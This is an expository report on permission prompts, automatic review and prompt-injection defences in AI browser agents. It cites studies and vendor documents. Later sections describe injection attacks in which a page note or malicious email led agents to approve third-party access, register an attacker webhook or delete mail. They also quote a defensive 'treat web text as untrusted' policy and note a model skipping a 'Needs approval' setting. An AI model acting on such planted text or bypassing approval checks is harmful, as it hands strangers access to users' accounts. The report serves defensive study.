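Chrome asks before the agent opens some sensitive sites, such as those for banking or personal medical information. It checks the address against a fixed list, so this prompt doesn't depend on a model's judgment. Chrome also asks before the agent signs in with a password saved in Google Password Manager. The model never receives the password, and the user can later remove a site from the list of sites where Gemini may sign in automatically. But in a live session the user is often already signed in, and then the sign-in prompt doesn't appear.

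For purchases, payments, messages and other consequential actions, Parker wrote that the agent "will try to pause" and get permission or have the user complete the step. This is a weaker promise because Chrome has to recognize that an action is consequential, and a button marked "Continue" might place an order on one site but open another page on a different site. Google warns users that Gemini could complete a purchase without their permission.

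OpenAI separates website access from sensitive actions most clearly in ChatGPT's cloud browser, which runs on a remote computer with its own cookies and sign-ins rather than in the user's live session. According to OpenAI's undated page *Using cloud browser in ChatGPT*, the user can review every new website, have ChatGPT check the address and ask only if it seems unsafe, or allow every site. Choices for individual sites override this setting. Under all three options, ChatGPT should still ask before an action that is hard to reverse or creates a real-world commitment, such as confirming a booking.

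OpenAI's June documentation for the Codex extension contains no similar promise. It describes confirmations for websites and browsing history, but not for payments or messages. Codex may still ask before making payments or sending messages, since the third-party copy of its instructions requires confirmation for some unspecified actions.

The table compares the rules that the vendors publish. The entries for Claude date from December 2026, and those for Chrome from December 2025 and July 2026. Microsoft's page and OpenAI's page about the cloud browser are undated.

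| Step | Claude in Chrome | Chrome auto browse | Edge with Copilot | ChatGPT cloud browser |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Making a purchase | Prohibited | Asks or hands over | Asks the user to supervise | Asks |
| Sending a message | No rule for every mode | Asks or hands over | Asks the user to supervise an email | Asks if the message is hard to reverse or makes a commitment |
| Deleting something permanently | Needs permission | May count as consequential | Asks the user to supervise deleting a calendar event | Asks |
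| Creating an account | Prohibited | May hand over | No specific rule | Asks if it creates a commitment |
| Opening a bank's site | Asks | Asks | Asks the user to watch or take over | Follows the website setting |

Google and Microsoft both require the user's involvement when an agent sends an email, but sending email isn't on Claude's lists for every mode. In automatic mode, Claude may therefore send one without a prompt if the message passes a review of whether it matches the request. Anthropic advises users to watch closely or return to manual approval when a task involves money, important files or messages sent in their name.

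Atlas once offered a logged-out mode in which the agent used none of the browser's existing cookies, according to OpenAI's *Using Ask ChatGPT sidebar and ChatGPT agent on Atlas*. Without those cookies, an agent can't send mail from the user's account even if it misjudges a request. The Chrome extension can't easily replace that mode because it uses the signed-in profile. The closest replacement is the desktop app's built-in browser, which by default also asks before using a new website, according to OpenAI.

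### A worked example: twelve actions on two sites

Suppose the agent completes a new copy of the expense form in its own tabs, taking six actions on each site. In the webmail, it opens the inbox, clicks the search box, types "invoice", opens the message, opens the attached invoice in the browser, and scrolls to the total. In the expense system, it opens the site, starts a claim, enters the total, enters the date, enters the user's home address from the invoice, and saves a draft.

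The counts below depend on several assumptions:

- The user is signed in to both sites, hasn't approved either one before, and approves everything the agent asks for.
- The webmail is a popular site and the expense system isn't. Neither is on a vendor's list of financial or otherwise restricted sites.
- The home address counts as sensitive information, and the original request doesn't count as explicit permission to enter it.
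- The automatic review blocks nothing.
- A request to watch the agent counts as one prompt.

| Product and mode | Prompts | What the user approves |
|---|---|---|
| Claude, manual approval in the newer panel, one action at a time | 12 | Every action |
| Claude, manual approval in the newer panel, one site at a time | 3 | Each site, then the address |
| Claude, manual approval in the classic panel | 2 | The plan, then the address |
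| Claude, automatic approval | 1 | The address |
| Claude, skipping all approvals | 0 or 1 | Possibly the address |
| Codex, default setting | 2 | Each site |
| Codex, "always allow browser content" | 0 | Nothing |
| Edge, Strict, always allowing each site | 3 | Each site, and a request to watch in the webmail |
| Edge, Balanced | 2 | The expense system, and a request to watch in the webmail |
| Edge, Light | 1 | A request to watch in the webmail |
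| Chrome auto browse | 0 | Nothing |

The totals for Codex and Chrome could each be one higher if that product requires confirmation before entering a home address. In Edge's Strict mode, a user who allowed only one action at a time would have to approve all twelve actions. ChatGPT's cloud browser would ask about both sites by default, and the user would also have to sign in to each one the first time.

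If a longer task took sixty actions on the same two sites, approving them one at a time would mean sixty prompts. The other counts would stay the same as long as the extra actions weren't sensitive.

Two modes with the same number of prompts can protect different things. Codex's two prompts name websites, so the user never specifically approves entering the address. In Claude's classic panel, the user approves a plan that covers both sites and then approves entering the address separately. Claude's automatic mode prompts only once, but it does so for the step that discloses personal information.

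If the agent submits the claim instead of saving a draft, a user who approves actions one at a time would see a prompt. Chrome might also show one if it treats the submission as consequential. But submitting a form isn't on Claude's lists or among Microsoft's examples, and a Codex user who has approved the expense system may get no further prompt. In automatic mode, Claude's review should catch the submission if the user asked only for a draft. It would probably be less likely to catch a wrong total, because the user did ask the agent to enter a total.

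### Michael and Roesner's study

In *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) examined how people control AI agents more generally. They reviewed 21 proposed permission systems, nearly all from research papers, and tested five commercial agents. For each proposal, they recorded how users state their rules, how the system translates those rules into a form software can apply, and how it enforces them.

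The 21 proposals had three main aims, and none achieved all three. Twelve tried to reduce the user's work, for instance by letting people write rules in ordinary language or by predicting the rules from the request. Eleven defined their rules formally, which makes them precise enough for software to analyze. Twelve used deterministic enforcement, where ordinary code or the user, rather than a model, makes the decision.

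In Cellmate, a proposal for browser agents, a model predicts the rules from the user's request and ordinary code enforces them. For the expense task, such a system might let the agent read the webmail and type in the expense system but block it from the bank, all without asking the user anything. The weakness is that the code enforces whatever the model predicts, so if the model wrongly includes the bank, the code will let the agent use it.

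In late May and early June 2026, the researchers tested the commercial products: the Claude chatbot, Claude Cowork, ChatGPT's chat and agent modes, and Codex. If an agent had permissions to grant, they granted a few, such as access to a folder or to a Gmail account created for the study. They gave each agent tasks under every available setting, then withdrew the permissions and tried again.

Michael and Roesner concluded that the products tended towards two extremes. Either the user had to answer frequent prompts, or a model made decisions that the user could barely see or control. ChatGPT showed both. Its chat mode required approval for every action that a permission covered, and the user could not approve actions in advance. Its agent mode worked in a remote browser with no permission settings, where it used Gmail freely.

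Claude sometimes switched between the two without telling the user. The researchers set its permission for creating email drafts to "Needs approval", but Claude created a draft without asking. The browser's log recorded that the action required no approval, and Claude said it had inferred permission from the request. The researchers reproduced this at least three times in June and July and reported it to Anthropic on 2 July.

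Claude's inference was arguably reasonable, since the researchers had asked it to write an email. But people who choose "Needs approval" expect to decide for themselves. The only other settings were "Always allow" and "Blocked", so the user couldn't prevent such inferences without blocking the tool.

Codex's automatic review was more transparent. The user had to turn it on and could turn it off at any time. But the setting applied to every tool in the session, so the user couldn't have a model review web searches while personally approving emails.

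#### Withdrawing access

The researchers found no way to withdraw a folder permission from Claude Cowork within the app. A new session started without the permission, but an older one kept it and could use it again if the user reopened that session. The only permanent ways they found to revoke the permission were the operating system's controls, where available, and uninstalling the app. Only six of the 21 research proposals clearly let users change or revoke a permission later. Michael and Roesner also cite an earlier survey of 18 web agents that found missing or deceptive options for revoking access.

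These results don't transfer directly to a live session. The only browser agent in the study used a remote browser. Cowork's folder permissions are also separate from the site permissions in Claude's extension, which users can revoke in the extension's settings. But the extension's newer side panel also runs as a Cowork session, and users can reopen old sessions there too. Someone should test whether a site permission that the user has since revoked still applies in a reopened session.

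The cloud browser lets the user withdraw access more thoroughly. Clearing a website's data there signs the agent out of the site but leaves the user signed in on their own computer. In a live session, signing the agent out also signs out the user.

Products have also changed since the tests. OpenAI's cloud browser now has the website settings that the remote browser lacked in June. Site permissions, as in Codex and Edge, fall between the two extremes because two or three prompts can cover a whole task, but each approval covers far more than the user needs. None of the site prompts described above lets the user allow the agent to type in the expense system but not submit anything.

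### The vendors' case for automatic review

OpenAI and Anthropic both argue that constant permission prompts make users less safe. The companies are defending features they sell, but they have published more evidence about these features than any other vendor discussed here. Most of that evidence comes from coding agents.

*Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) explains OpenAI's reasoning that users who tire of prompts may turn off the restrictions entirely, write rules that are far too broad, or approve commands they don't understand. A sizable minority of Codex users inside OpenAI had allowed every command beginning with "python", which lets the agent run almost anything. Anthropic reports a similar pattern in Claude Code, where users approve 97% of permission prompts and a quarter of interactive sessions start with permission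 checks bypassed.

If users behave this way, the realistic alternative to automatic review is often no review. OpenAI also uses a separate model for the review because the main agent's goal is to finish the task, so it may treat a permission check as an obstacle. The reviewer only has to decide whether the action should go ahead.

In OpenAI's tests, Codex stopped for human approval roughly 200 times less often with automatic review than with manual approval. In an illustrative sample of 10,000 actions, 9,280 stayed inside Codex's sandbox, a restricted area where it can edit certain files and run local commands without permission. The other 720 would each have interrupted the user in manual mode. The automatic reviewer approved 713 of them and rejected seven. Codex found a safer alternative in four of the rejected cases and stopped to ask the user in the other three.

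A live browser session has no equivalent of that sandbox. Codex can change a local file many times before anyone else sees it, but a click in the user's webmail may immediately send or delete a message. A browser reviewer therefore has to judge a much larger share of the agent's actions, and the 200-fold reduction may not apply. OpenAI keeps some decisions with the user. According to its *Auto-review*, the reviewer doesn't handle prompts for access to apps through Computer Use, which lets the agent operate other programs.

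The reviewer also makes mistakes. It rejected 90.3% of artificial test cases in which the agent was overeager, for example by transferring data the user hadn't meant to share or doing something irreversible, and allowed the rest. Trębacz and colleagues also found ways to mislead it and warn against treating it as a guarantee.

Anthropic compared manual approval with automatic review in real Claude Code sessions from May and June 2026. In sessions already flagged by Anthropic's safety systems, a model graded how harmful the agent's actions were and whether the user had explicitly asked for them. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested appeared in 6.3% of the manually approved sessions and 2.4% of those with automatic review. Anthropic counted harm as serious if it was at least comparable to deleting rows from a company's live database.

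This comparison supports automatic review, but it doesn't prove that the review caused the difference. Users chose their own modes, and those who preferred manual approval may have been doing riskier work. The percentages also cover only flagged sessions, so they aren't rates for ordinary use. Anthropic also found that Team and Enterprise customers who adopted automatic mode produced about 25% more code submissions, but they may have chosen that mode because they delegate more work to the agent.

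Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome is generally available* reports that, with automatic review and a separate scan for malicious content, no attacks in the company's current test set succeeded against Claude Opus 5 or Sonnet 5, and 0.3% succeeded against Fable 5. Anthropic hasn't published how often the review catches an agent's ordinary mistakes in the browser, such as picking the wrong invoice or typing over something the user wanted to keep.

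Automatic review can be more transparent than Michael and Roesner found it. OpenAI publishes the policy that Codex's reviewer follows, so an expert user can check what the reviewer should block. A browser agent could also give the user a list of the actions its reviewer had approved, with the website and the reason for each.

Whether automatic approval makes a user safer depends on what it replaces. It adds a check for someone who used to skip every approval, but someone who used Claude's classic panel and read its plans loses the chance to rule out a website before the task begins.

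## Do permission prompts lead to real decisions?

A click on "Allow" shows that the user approved a request, but not that they made a real decision. To make one, the user has to understand what the agent is about to do, and the request has to be specific enough that they aren't approving other actions as well. The user also has to be able to refuse without giving up the whole task, and to withdraw approval later.

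A prompt asking permission to type 84.20 into the empty Total field of the March claim can meet all these conditions. The user can compare the figure with the invoice, refuse and type it themselves, or delete it afterward. *Security and Privacy in Agentic AI* (Jenkins, Kitkowska and colleagues, 2026), a report on a workshop of thirty experts, sets similar requirements for human oversight in general. The person responsible needs the power to intervene, access to the relevant facts, the authority to act and a procedure to follow.

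### Why long tasks make approval harder

A permission prompt may leave out facts from earlier steps that the user needs to make a decision. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to reconcile supplier invoices and send an outside auditor only the summary totals. Instructions planted in a vendor's note lead the agent to fill a file named report.csv with the individual rows of the invoices. When the agent requests approval to send the auditor this file, the recipient and file name look right, but the prompt doesn't show that the file contains data the user said not to send.

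Long tasks also lead products to offer broader approvals, because users don't want to answer sixty specific prompts. *Options, Not Clicks* (2026) criticizes systems that offer only "Allow" and "Always Allow" for each of the agent's tools. A user who chooses "Always Allow" for email approves every future message the agent sends, regardless of the recipient or attachments.

Refusing a step causes the user almost no trouble at the start of a task, but more as the work proceeds. A user who refuses the nineteenth of twenty steps, for example, may have to work out how to finish a half-completed claim by hand.

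Withdrawing approval is difficult partly because the options for it are often missing or deceptive, as Zhang and Wang found in their survey of 18 web agents for CHI 2026, a human-computer interaction conference. According to Michael and Roesner, the survey also found that permissions were too coarse and that the access that took effect in the system was broader than what users authorized in a particular interaction. Chrome's connection dialog also has this mismatch between authorization and access.

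### How people learn to click through

*How to Ask for Permission* (Felt, Egelman and colleagues, 2012) explains careless approvals with a model from research on how people answer closed questions. People who are optimizing read the question, recall what they know and decide, while people who are satisficing rely on a few cues and a simple rule, such as "clicking Yes makes the box go away". Repetition moves people from optimizing to satisficing. Researchers call this habituation, and those who study agents often call it approval fatigue or prompt fatigue.

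The habit also carries over to similar-looking prompts. A new user of a browser agent has already dismissed years of license agreements and cookie notices, so they may settle for a quick, good-enough answer from the agent's first prompt onward.

Some of the strongest evidence comes from User Account Control, the Windows dialog that asks the user to approve a program's request for greater privileges. In a 2010 study by Motiee and colleagues, participants saw fake versions of the dialog while completing other tasks. According to slides by Felt and colleagues, 95% of participants consented. This is more worrying than a high approval rate in ordinary use, because participants should have refused these requests.

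On Android phones at the time, users had to accept all the permissions an app requested or not install it. In Felt's research, 42% of participants had never noticed these permissions. In a message that Langel (2012) quoted on a web standards mailing list, Felt estimated that about 18% of people looked at the permissions for a given installation and about 60% looked occasionally. Most had no idea what the permissions meant. Fewer prompts alone would not have solved the problem, because people did not understand the requests, in addition to not reading them.

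Browser warnings have a better record. *Alice in Warningland* (Akhawe and Felt, 2013) analyzed more than 25 million security warnings shown in Chrome and Firefox. Users continued past about a tenth of Firefox's malware and phishing warnings and about a quarter of Chrome's. For warnings about insecure connections, they continued past a third of Firefox's and 70.2% of Chrome's, so the design of a warning seems to matter a great deal. Continuing past a connection warning isn't always a bad decision, because a badly configured but harmless website can trigger the same warning as an attack.

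### Choosing how to ask

Felt and colleagues argued that a platform should choose a method separately for each permission. Besides dialogs and install-time warnings, they considered automatic grants and trusted controls. A trusted control is a button, chooser or review screen that only the platform can draw, and using it grants the permission. When a user selects two albums in a phone's photo chooser, for example, the app receives those albums and nothing else. The choice of method depends on up to five questions, in this order:

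1. Can the user undo the action with little effort? If so, grant the permission automatically.
2. Would abuse of the permission be merely annoying? If so, grant it automatically.
3. Did the user start the request? If so, use a trusted control.
4. Can the user alter the action, for instance by choosing which photos to share? If so, use a trusted control.
5. Does the action have to work later, without the user's immediate approval? If so, ask at installation. If not, use a run-time dialog.

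The researchers applied these questions to 83 smartphone permissions, after surveying 3,115 smartphone users to find out which risks they considered minor. They assigned 55% of the permissions to automatic grants, 23% to trusted controls, 16% to run-time dialogs and 6% to install-time warnings. When they checked the twenty most popular free iPhone apps against this scheme, the apps needed an average of only 0.25 run-time dialogs each. They didn't test whether people made better decisions under the scheme.

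The same questions can be applied to the expense task:

| Action | What decides it | Method |
|---|---|---|
| Opening an agent tab | The user can close the tab | Automatic grant, with a label on the tab so the user knows who opened it |
| Claiming a user tab | The user can't undo what the agent reads or erases, but can choose the tab | A tab picker that the browser controls |
| Submitting a form | The user can't easily take the claim back, but can change it first | A review screen, with the last click left to the user |

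The automatic grant should cover only the new tab. Access to a sensitive website should still require separate permission, because closing the tab doesn't undo what the agent has read there.

The iPhone already handled text messages the way the table suggests for forms. An app could write a message and choose the recipient, but the phone then showed the user an editable preview and sent nothing until the user pressed the send button. This is harder in a browser, where the website provides the "Submit" button and the harness can't always detect which click submits the form. When it can't, the harness can fall back on a run-time dialog.

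If the user is away, the only remaining option is approval in advance. Felt and colleagues treat this as a last resort. It works especially badly for forms, because the user would be approving a claim before the agent had filled it in.

### People supervising agents

The study closest to a live session is *Dark Patterns Meet GUI Agents* by Tang, Chen and colleagues (2025). They built 16 test websites, each with one manipulative design, such as a pre-ticked box that shares the user's data. Each of 22 participants completed eight tasks alone and supervised OpenAI's browser agent, Operator, on eight others by watching recordings. Participants could pause the video, let it continue to approve the agent's actions, or skip the task to refuse.

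When the agent explicitly asked for confirmation, such as before placing an order, participants almost always examined the action first. Otherwise, they tended to accept what the agent did unless something looked wrong. Supervised tasks went better for ten of the 16 deceptive designs and worse for two, and nobody fell for the other four in either condition. For pre-ticked boxes and similar defaults, the share of participants who avoided the deception rose from 33% to 80%. Part of this improvement may be due to Operator itself, which was the best of the six agents the researchers had tested. Participants could also skip a task without losing any work of their own.

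Supervising the agent narrowed what people looked at. Four participants considered only the item the agent had selected, and two inspected only the tab it had opened, so they missed alternatives in other tabs. A user watching the agent's tab this closely might not notice the agent reloading an expense form in another tab.

Two larger studies used simulated assistants that handled email, documents and purchases, not browser agents. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people from outside the software industry supervised an assistant through a scripted day of 18 actions. Seven of these went beyond the task, such as reading the user's bank transactions to help with a trip budget. One group approved or denied each action.

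Hossain and colleagues had 80 volunteers make 12 decisions each, half of them about requests that broke the user's instructions. Each volunteer saw one of four kinds of prompt. The first briefly described the next action. The second added the action's exact details, and the third also included the user's original instruction and a log of everything the agent had done. The fourth presented the same facts as the third, organized around the action's consequences. In the auditor example, the fourth prompt showed the user that the agent had built the attachment from raw invoice rows.

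| Prompt | Proper actions approved | Improper actions approved |
|---|---|---|
| Yan, a prompt for every action | 94% | 40% |
| Hossain and colleagues, short description | 92% | 55% |
| The same study, with exact details | 90% | 43% |
| The same study, with the instruction and a log | 88% | 33% |
| The same study, arranged by consequence | 86% | 24% |

In every row, people approved proper actions far more often than improper ones, so they weren't approving requests blindly. But they still approved between a quarter and a half of the requests they should have refused. Some of the approvals Yan counts as mistakes were sensible. Of the 34 people in that group, 30 let the assistant call the airport to confirm a flight, which the task hadn't asked for but many travelers would welcome. Twelve people in the group let it read their bank transactions, which is harder to explain.

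Most of the improvement in Hossain's study came from giving people more facts. Arranging the facts by consequence may have helped further, but after statistical adjustment, the difference from the log ranged from 20 percentage points better to 4 points worse. Better prompts also slowed decisions, from a median of 16 seconds with the short description to 33 seconds with the consequence version. People can spare half a minute before sending a file to an auditor, but not before every click in a webmail search.

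### Evidence from coding tools

Much of the other recent evidence comes from software work. In *Looks Fine to Me*, Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues (2026) gave 36 people programming tasks with an agent whose code was sometimes correct, sometimes visibly broken, and sometimes defective in a way the available checks didn't catch. Participants readily spotted the visible failures, but they often missed the hidden defects while remaining highly confident. Some ran checks that couldn't have revealed the problem, and others had the evidence but misread it.

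A wrong invoice total is also a silent defect, because the expense system will accept either 48.20 or 84.20. A user who glances at the completed form and sees no error message may feel they have checked it.

*Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), based on interviews and a survey of software practitioners, found that how closely people watch an agent depends on the risk, how much they trust the agent, how much time they have and how tired they are. They also care whether they can undo an action, which supports Felt's choice to ask about that first.

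*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) reviews 290 reports of agents mishandling files. In 80 of them, users had turned on automatic approval, and 31 involved prompts that didn't make a command's effects clear. For instance, a user asked to approve `python3 setup.py` can't tell from the prompt what the script will do. Because the review covers only cases where something went wrong, it doesn't show how often automatic approval causes trouble.

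### What a high approval rate means

Anthropic's figure that users approve 97% of permission prompts also comes from a coding tool, Claude Code. None of the browser-agent vendors discussed here appears to have published an equivalent figure.

Even an approval rate for browser agents wouldn't be enough to judge whether users are making real decisions. Suppose a user sees 1,000 requests and should refuse 30 of them. A user who refuses exactly those 30 and a user who refuses 30 at random both approve 97%, but the second catches only about one bad request on average. To tell these users apart, a vendor would need to know which requests were bad. It could occasionally insert a harmless test request that the user should refuse, and check which approvals users later regret or reverse.

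The experiments avoid this problem because the researchers knew which actions were improper. But improper requests made up half of Hossain's cases and more than a third of Yan's, so participants had frequent reason to stay alert. People who rarely see improper requests may catch a smaller share of them.

### Remedies and their weaknesses

*Janus* (Brigham, Bagdasarian and colleagues, 2026) compared six designs for involving users in an agent's permissions across three scenarios. It found that user input can greatly strengthen privacy and security, and that AI help with the decisions can reduce mental effort, but no design was best in every scenario. The study used three kinds of simulated users, so it can show how a design copes with a tired user but not how tired real people become.

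#### Fewer prompts

Felt and colleagues recommend saving the user's attention for permissions with severe consequences. This should reduce habituation, but people who see fewer prompts don't necessarily become stricter. In Yan's experiment, a second group set rules in advance for spending money, sending information, deleting things and reading private data. They saw about 11 prompts instead of 18, but approved 67% of the actions outside the task that they were asked about, compared with 40% in the group that saw every prompt.

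This comparison is imperfect because people who had chosen "never" for a category no longer saw prompts about it, and Yan later recruited extra participants only for the group with rules. That group's choices are more telling. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, mostly putting off the decision, so the rules did little to reduce their reliance on prompts.

#### Approving a plan

A plan lets users object to a step before the task begins, but the agent writes the plan before reading the pages. In the auditor example, the user could approve a sensible plan to reconcile the invoices and send the totals, and the agent would find the malicious note only afterward.

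The harness therefore has to compare later actions with what the user approved. Hossain and colleagues built a monitor that records which data went into each file, without relying on the agent's reports. With one model, blocking every action that the monitor flagged or couldn't classify reduced runs with an unsafe action from 52 to 6 out of 120. It also reduced completed legitimate tasks from 104 to 100.

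The monitor depends on a complete record of what the agent did. When the researchers gave it only part of the record, the agent completed just 77% of legitimate tasks. This could be a serious problem in a browser, where an agent may read a number on one page and type it on another without creating a file to track.

#### Automatic review

For a third group in Yan's experiment, a model reviewed each action and either allowed it or referred it to the user. It allowed eight of the 11 actions the task required and referred all seven that went beyond it. Participants then approved those seven 46% of the time. A reviewer that catches every action that goes too far can still give little protection if the user approves too readily.

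If the reviewer blocks actions itself, the user can't allow one they want. In this group, 37 of 44 people approved the call to the airport. An alternative is to predict each user's choices. *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents* (Wu, Yang and colleagues, 2025) studied what influences people's permission decisions in order to automate them. Before every decision, participants got a reminder to be careful. A system that learned from everyday clicks would be learning from decisions made without that reminder, and if the user had been approving everything out of habit, it would learn to approve everything too.

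#### Granting access by gesture

A user who grants access by picking a tab or pressing a button as part of the task isn't interrupted. Felt and colleagues cite earlier work in which access granted through trusted controls matched people's expectations about privacy and security. In the expense task, the user would choose the March claim from a list and later press "Submit", looking at the relevant page both times.

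A gesture can't help when the user is away, and choosing a tab doesn't specify what the agent may do there. Developers may also avoid the method if they have an easier one. Android let apps send text messages either through a trusted control or by requesting a broad permission at installation, and developers often chose the broad permission even when their app didn't need it. A browser that offers agents a tab picker may therefore have to stop offering them access to every tab.

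## What still limits the agent when a web page misleads it?

A tab picker or a review screen protects the user only while they are looking at it. For the rest of the task, the agent reads text that strangers may have written and acts through the user's signed-in accounts. If a page contains misleading content, either the model has to detect it or something outside the model has to block the resulting action.

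### The confused deputy

Security researchers call a program in this position a confused deputy. The term comes from Hardy's 1988 description of a compiler, a program that translates source code into software. The compiler had permission to write to a billing file, and it let users name its output file. A user who entered the billing file's name could make the compiler overwrite it, because nothing checked whether the compiler's permission was meant for that use.

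A browser agent acts with the user's authority in a live session, but a web page can determine how the agent uses that authority. Suppose an email leads the agent to a page where an unfamiliar app requests access to the user's mailbox. If the agent clicks "Approve", the mail service receives a valid request with the user's cookie and has no obvious reason to refuse it. The app may then keep its access long after the agent has finished. Attackers already trick people into approving apps this way, a technique called consent phishing.

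Websites' defenses against two older forms of this problem do not stop a misled agent. In cross-site request forgery, a malicious page makes the browser send another site a request with the user's cookies attached. Sites prevent this by accepting only requests that come from their own forms. In clickjacking, a malicious page hides a genuine page inside a disguised frame so that the user unknowingly clicks a real button. Sites prevent this by refusing to load inside other sites' frames. A misled agent passes both checks because it opens the genuine page directly and submits the genuine form.

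### Approvals the user never requested

In *The Agent Clicks Approve*, Md Imran Hossen measured how often a page could get an agent to grant access that the user hadn't asked for. The tests, run in June 2026, used the open-source agent framework browser-use with either Claude Haiku 4.5 or GPT-5.5. All the websites ran on a local server that treated the agent's browser as signed in.

In one scenario, the user asked only for a summary of a page about exporting billing data. A two-sentence note on the page presented approving access as a step the work required, and linked to a page on another origin where a third-party app was requesting access to the account. In the other, the user asked the agent to complete any pending setup tasks in a guide. The guide gave an attacker-controlled address for a webhook, a setting that makes a service automatically send an account's events to an outside address.

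Without a defense, the agent completed the unauthorized action in all 73 attack runs, giving an approval in 53 and registering a webhook in 20. The attack note made the approval look like part of the user's task and never told the agent to ignore that task. In its final answers, the agent reported the approval as progress. With a harmless note instead, the agent did not try to grant access or register a webhook in any of 92 runs.

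The approval page did little to slow the agents down. In all 53 approvals, it displayed an access code containing the word "privileged". In ten, it also asked the reader to review the app, the account and the code before approving.

Each scenario used one direct, clearly visible note, so the 73 out of 73 isn't a general success rate. On a different version of the pages, an older model, GPT-5.4, approved access in only 4 of 10 runs. A less direct note in small print worked on Haiku 4.5 in 4 of 10 runs and never on GPT-5.4.

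#### A written policy

Telling the model not to do this may not stop it. Hossen gave Haiku 4.5 an explicit policy that only the user's task could authorize an approval, that text on web pages was untrusted, and that the model should refuse unrelated requests for access. The agent still approved access in 7 of 10 attack runs. The policy also interfered with legitimate approvals, since the agent failed to complete the approval in one of ten runs where the user had asked for it.

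With only ten runs, the 95% confidence interval for the attack's success rate is roughly 35% to 93%, so the policy may have stopped most attacks on these pages or almost none. The interval reflects only the variation between runs on one set of pages and doesn't measure how the policy would do on others.

The same policy did far better when the page's code marked the note as untrusted and the approval page used the standard technical vocabulary for such requests. Only 1 of 10 attacks succeeded on those pages. The two sets of pages differed in several ways, so the experiment can't show which cues mattered. But real attackers don't label their notes, so a developer who tested the policy only on the labeled pages would have greatly overestimated how well it works.

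### How often attacks succeed on newer models

In October, Pogorelec (2026) reported on Haiku 5.5, the successor to Anthropic's small model Haiku 4.5, in *Anthropic's new budget model gets much better at ignoring hidden commands*. Anthropic's larger models have also improved a great deal since the company began testing its Chrome extension.

In one of Anthropic's 2025 tests of the extension, a malicious email claimed that messages had to be deleted for security reasons, and Claude deleted the user's email without asking. The table compares that year's results with later ones. Anthropic used an automated attacker in the November test that tried and combined many known techniques. The 2026 figures come from Anthropic's system cards, the safety reports it publishes with new models, as reported by VentureBeat for Opus 4.8 and The Decoder for Opus 5.

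| Date | Version of Claude | Test | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| August 2025 | Pilot of the Chrome extension | 123 cases | 23.6% before new defenses, 11.2% after |
| November 2025 | Opus 4.5 | An attacker with 100 attempts | 8.0% for the model alone, 1.4% with safeguards |
| May 2026 | Opus 4.8, with extended thinking on | 129 scenarios, ten attempts at each | 31.5% of attempts for the model alone, 0.5% with safeguards |
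| July 2026 | Opus 5 | 129 scenarios | 0% |

These tests differ, so the rise from 8.0% to 31.5% doesn't mean that the model itself became easier to attack. In the May test, the older Sonnet 4.6 scored 50.7% without safeguards. In the same test, Opus 4.8 scored 31.5% without safeguards and 0.5% with them, so most of its protection came from the safeguards. A developer who builds an agent on the same model without them can't expect the 0.5% figure.

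Later releases appear to have kept the gains. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Fable 5.1, dated 1 September, describes its counterpart, Mythos 5.1, as the company's most robust model so far on an outside test of prompt injection. Three weeks later, Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Opus 5.5 reported results similar to or better than Opus 5's on every such test, but also found the new model more likely than earlier ones to follow some malicious instructions. Both cards predate Fable 5.2 and Mythos 5.2, which Anthropic announced on 9 November in *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026).

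#### What a rate near zero means

A success rate per attempt understates the danger from an attacker who can keep trying. If each attempt had an independent 0.5% chance of success, the chance that at least one of 100 would succeed would be 1 − 0.995¹⁰⁰, or about 39%. Real attempts aren't independent, because some pages and phrasings work much better than others, but a rate per attempt still needs to be paired with a figure that accounts for repeated attempts. Anthropic also counts the share of scenarios in which any attempt succeeded, which is a harder test for the agent.

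The true success rate could still be above zero even though no attack succeeded in the 129 scenarios. If it were 2% per scenario, a test of this size would find no successes about 7% of the time. That assumes the scenarios are a fair sample of real attacks, but attackers look for whatever the test left out. The Decoder reports that on a more general test by the security company Gray Swan, attackers succeeded against Opus 5 in 2.0% of cases after 15 attempts, down from 5.5% for Opus 4.8.

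With these improvements, a user of a current model faces far less risk than the 2025 figures suggest. But the remaining failures matter more in a live session than elsewhere, because a single one may give a stranger lasting access to a mailbox. Several researchers and vendors have therefore built limits that still work when an attack on the model succeeds.

### A check at the service

Hossen's own remedy moves the decision to the website that would carry out the action. Three facts identify a request for access:

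- the **client**, meaning the app that wants access
- the **account** it wants to reach
- the **scope**, meaning what it may do there

The client, account and scope of a request form a tuple, or ordered list. Before the agent opens any page, the service receives the set of tuples that the user's task allows, which Hossen calls the task's authority envelope. The service accepts a request only if the request's tuple is in that set.

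Suppose a user asks the agent to connect an app named Receipt Reader to their work expense account so the app can read receipts. The envelope contains one tuple, (Receipt Reader, work account, read receipts). A full check would treat four requests as follows.

| Client | Account | Scope | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Receipt Reader | Work | Read receipts | Accepted |
| Receipt Reader | Personal | Read receipts | Rejected, wrong account |
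| Invoice Helper | Work | Read receipts | Rejected, wrong app |
| Receipt Reader | Work | Read receipts and submit claims | Rejected, too much access |

If the user had asked the agent only to put an invoice total in a form, the envelope would be empty, and the service would reject all four.

The version in the experiment was slightly weaker. It compared the client and account with the task but took the scope from the service's own record of what the app had requested, so an app that asked for too much from the start could have passed. Hossen notes that a real deployment would need to include the scope in the envelope.

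With the check in place, the agents sent the unauthorized request in all 70 attack runs, and the service rejected it every time. The rejections were expected, because the envelope was empty and the agent had no other way to complete the action, but they confirm that the check doesn't depend on the model's behavior. The service also allowed the action in all 73 control runs, where the user's task named it, which shows that the check doesn't simply block everything.

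Another test shows why the tuple must include the account. The user's task named one account, but the page asked for access to another with a similar name. Haiku 4.5 submitted the request for the wrong account in all five runs, and the service rejected it each time. GPT-5.5 noticed the mismatch in all eight of its runs and submitted nothing. A better model can compare the accounts itself, but the service rejected the wrong one even when the model did not.

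#### After the rejection

Blocking the request didn't end the attack. The agents often tried again, sending 103 requests over the 70 runs. In 49 of the 53 blocked approval runs, the agent's final answer listed approving the access as a next step for the reader. In two others, it wrongly stated that the access had been approved.

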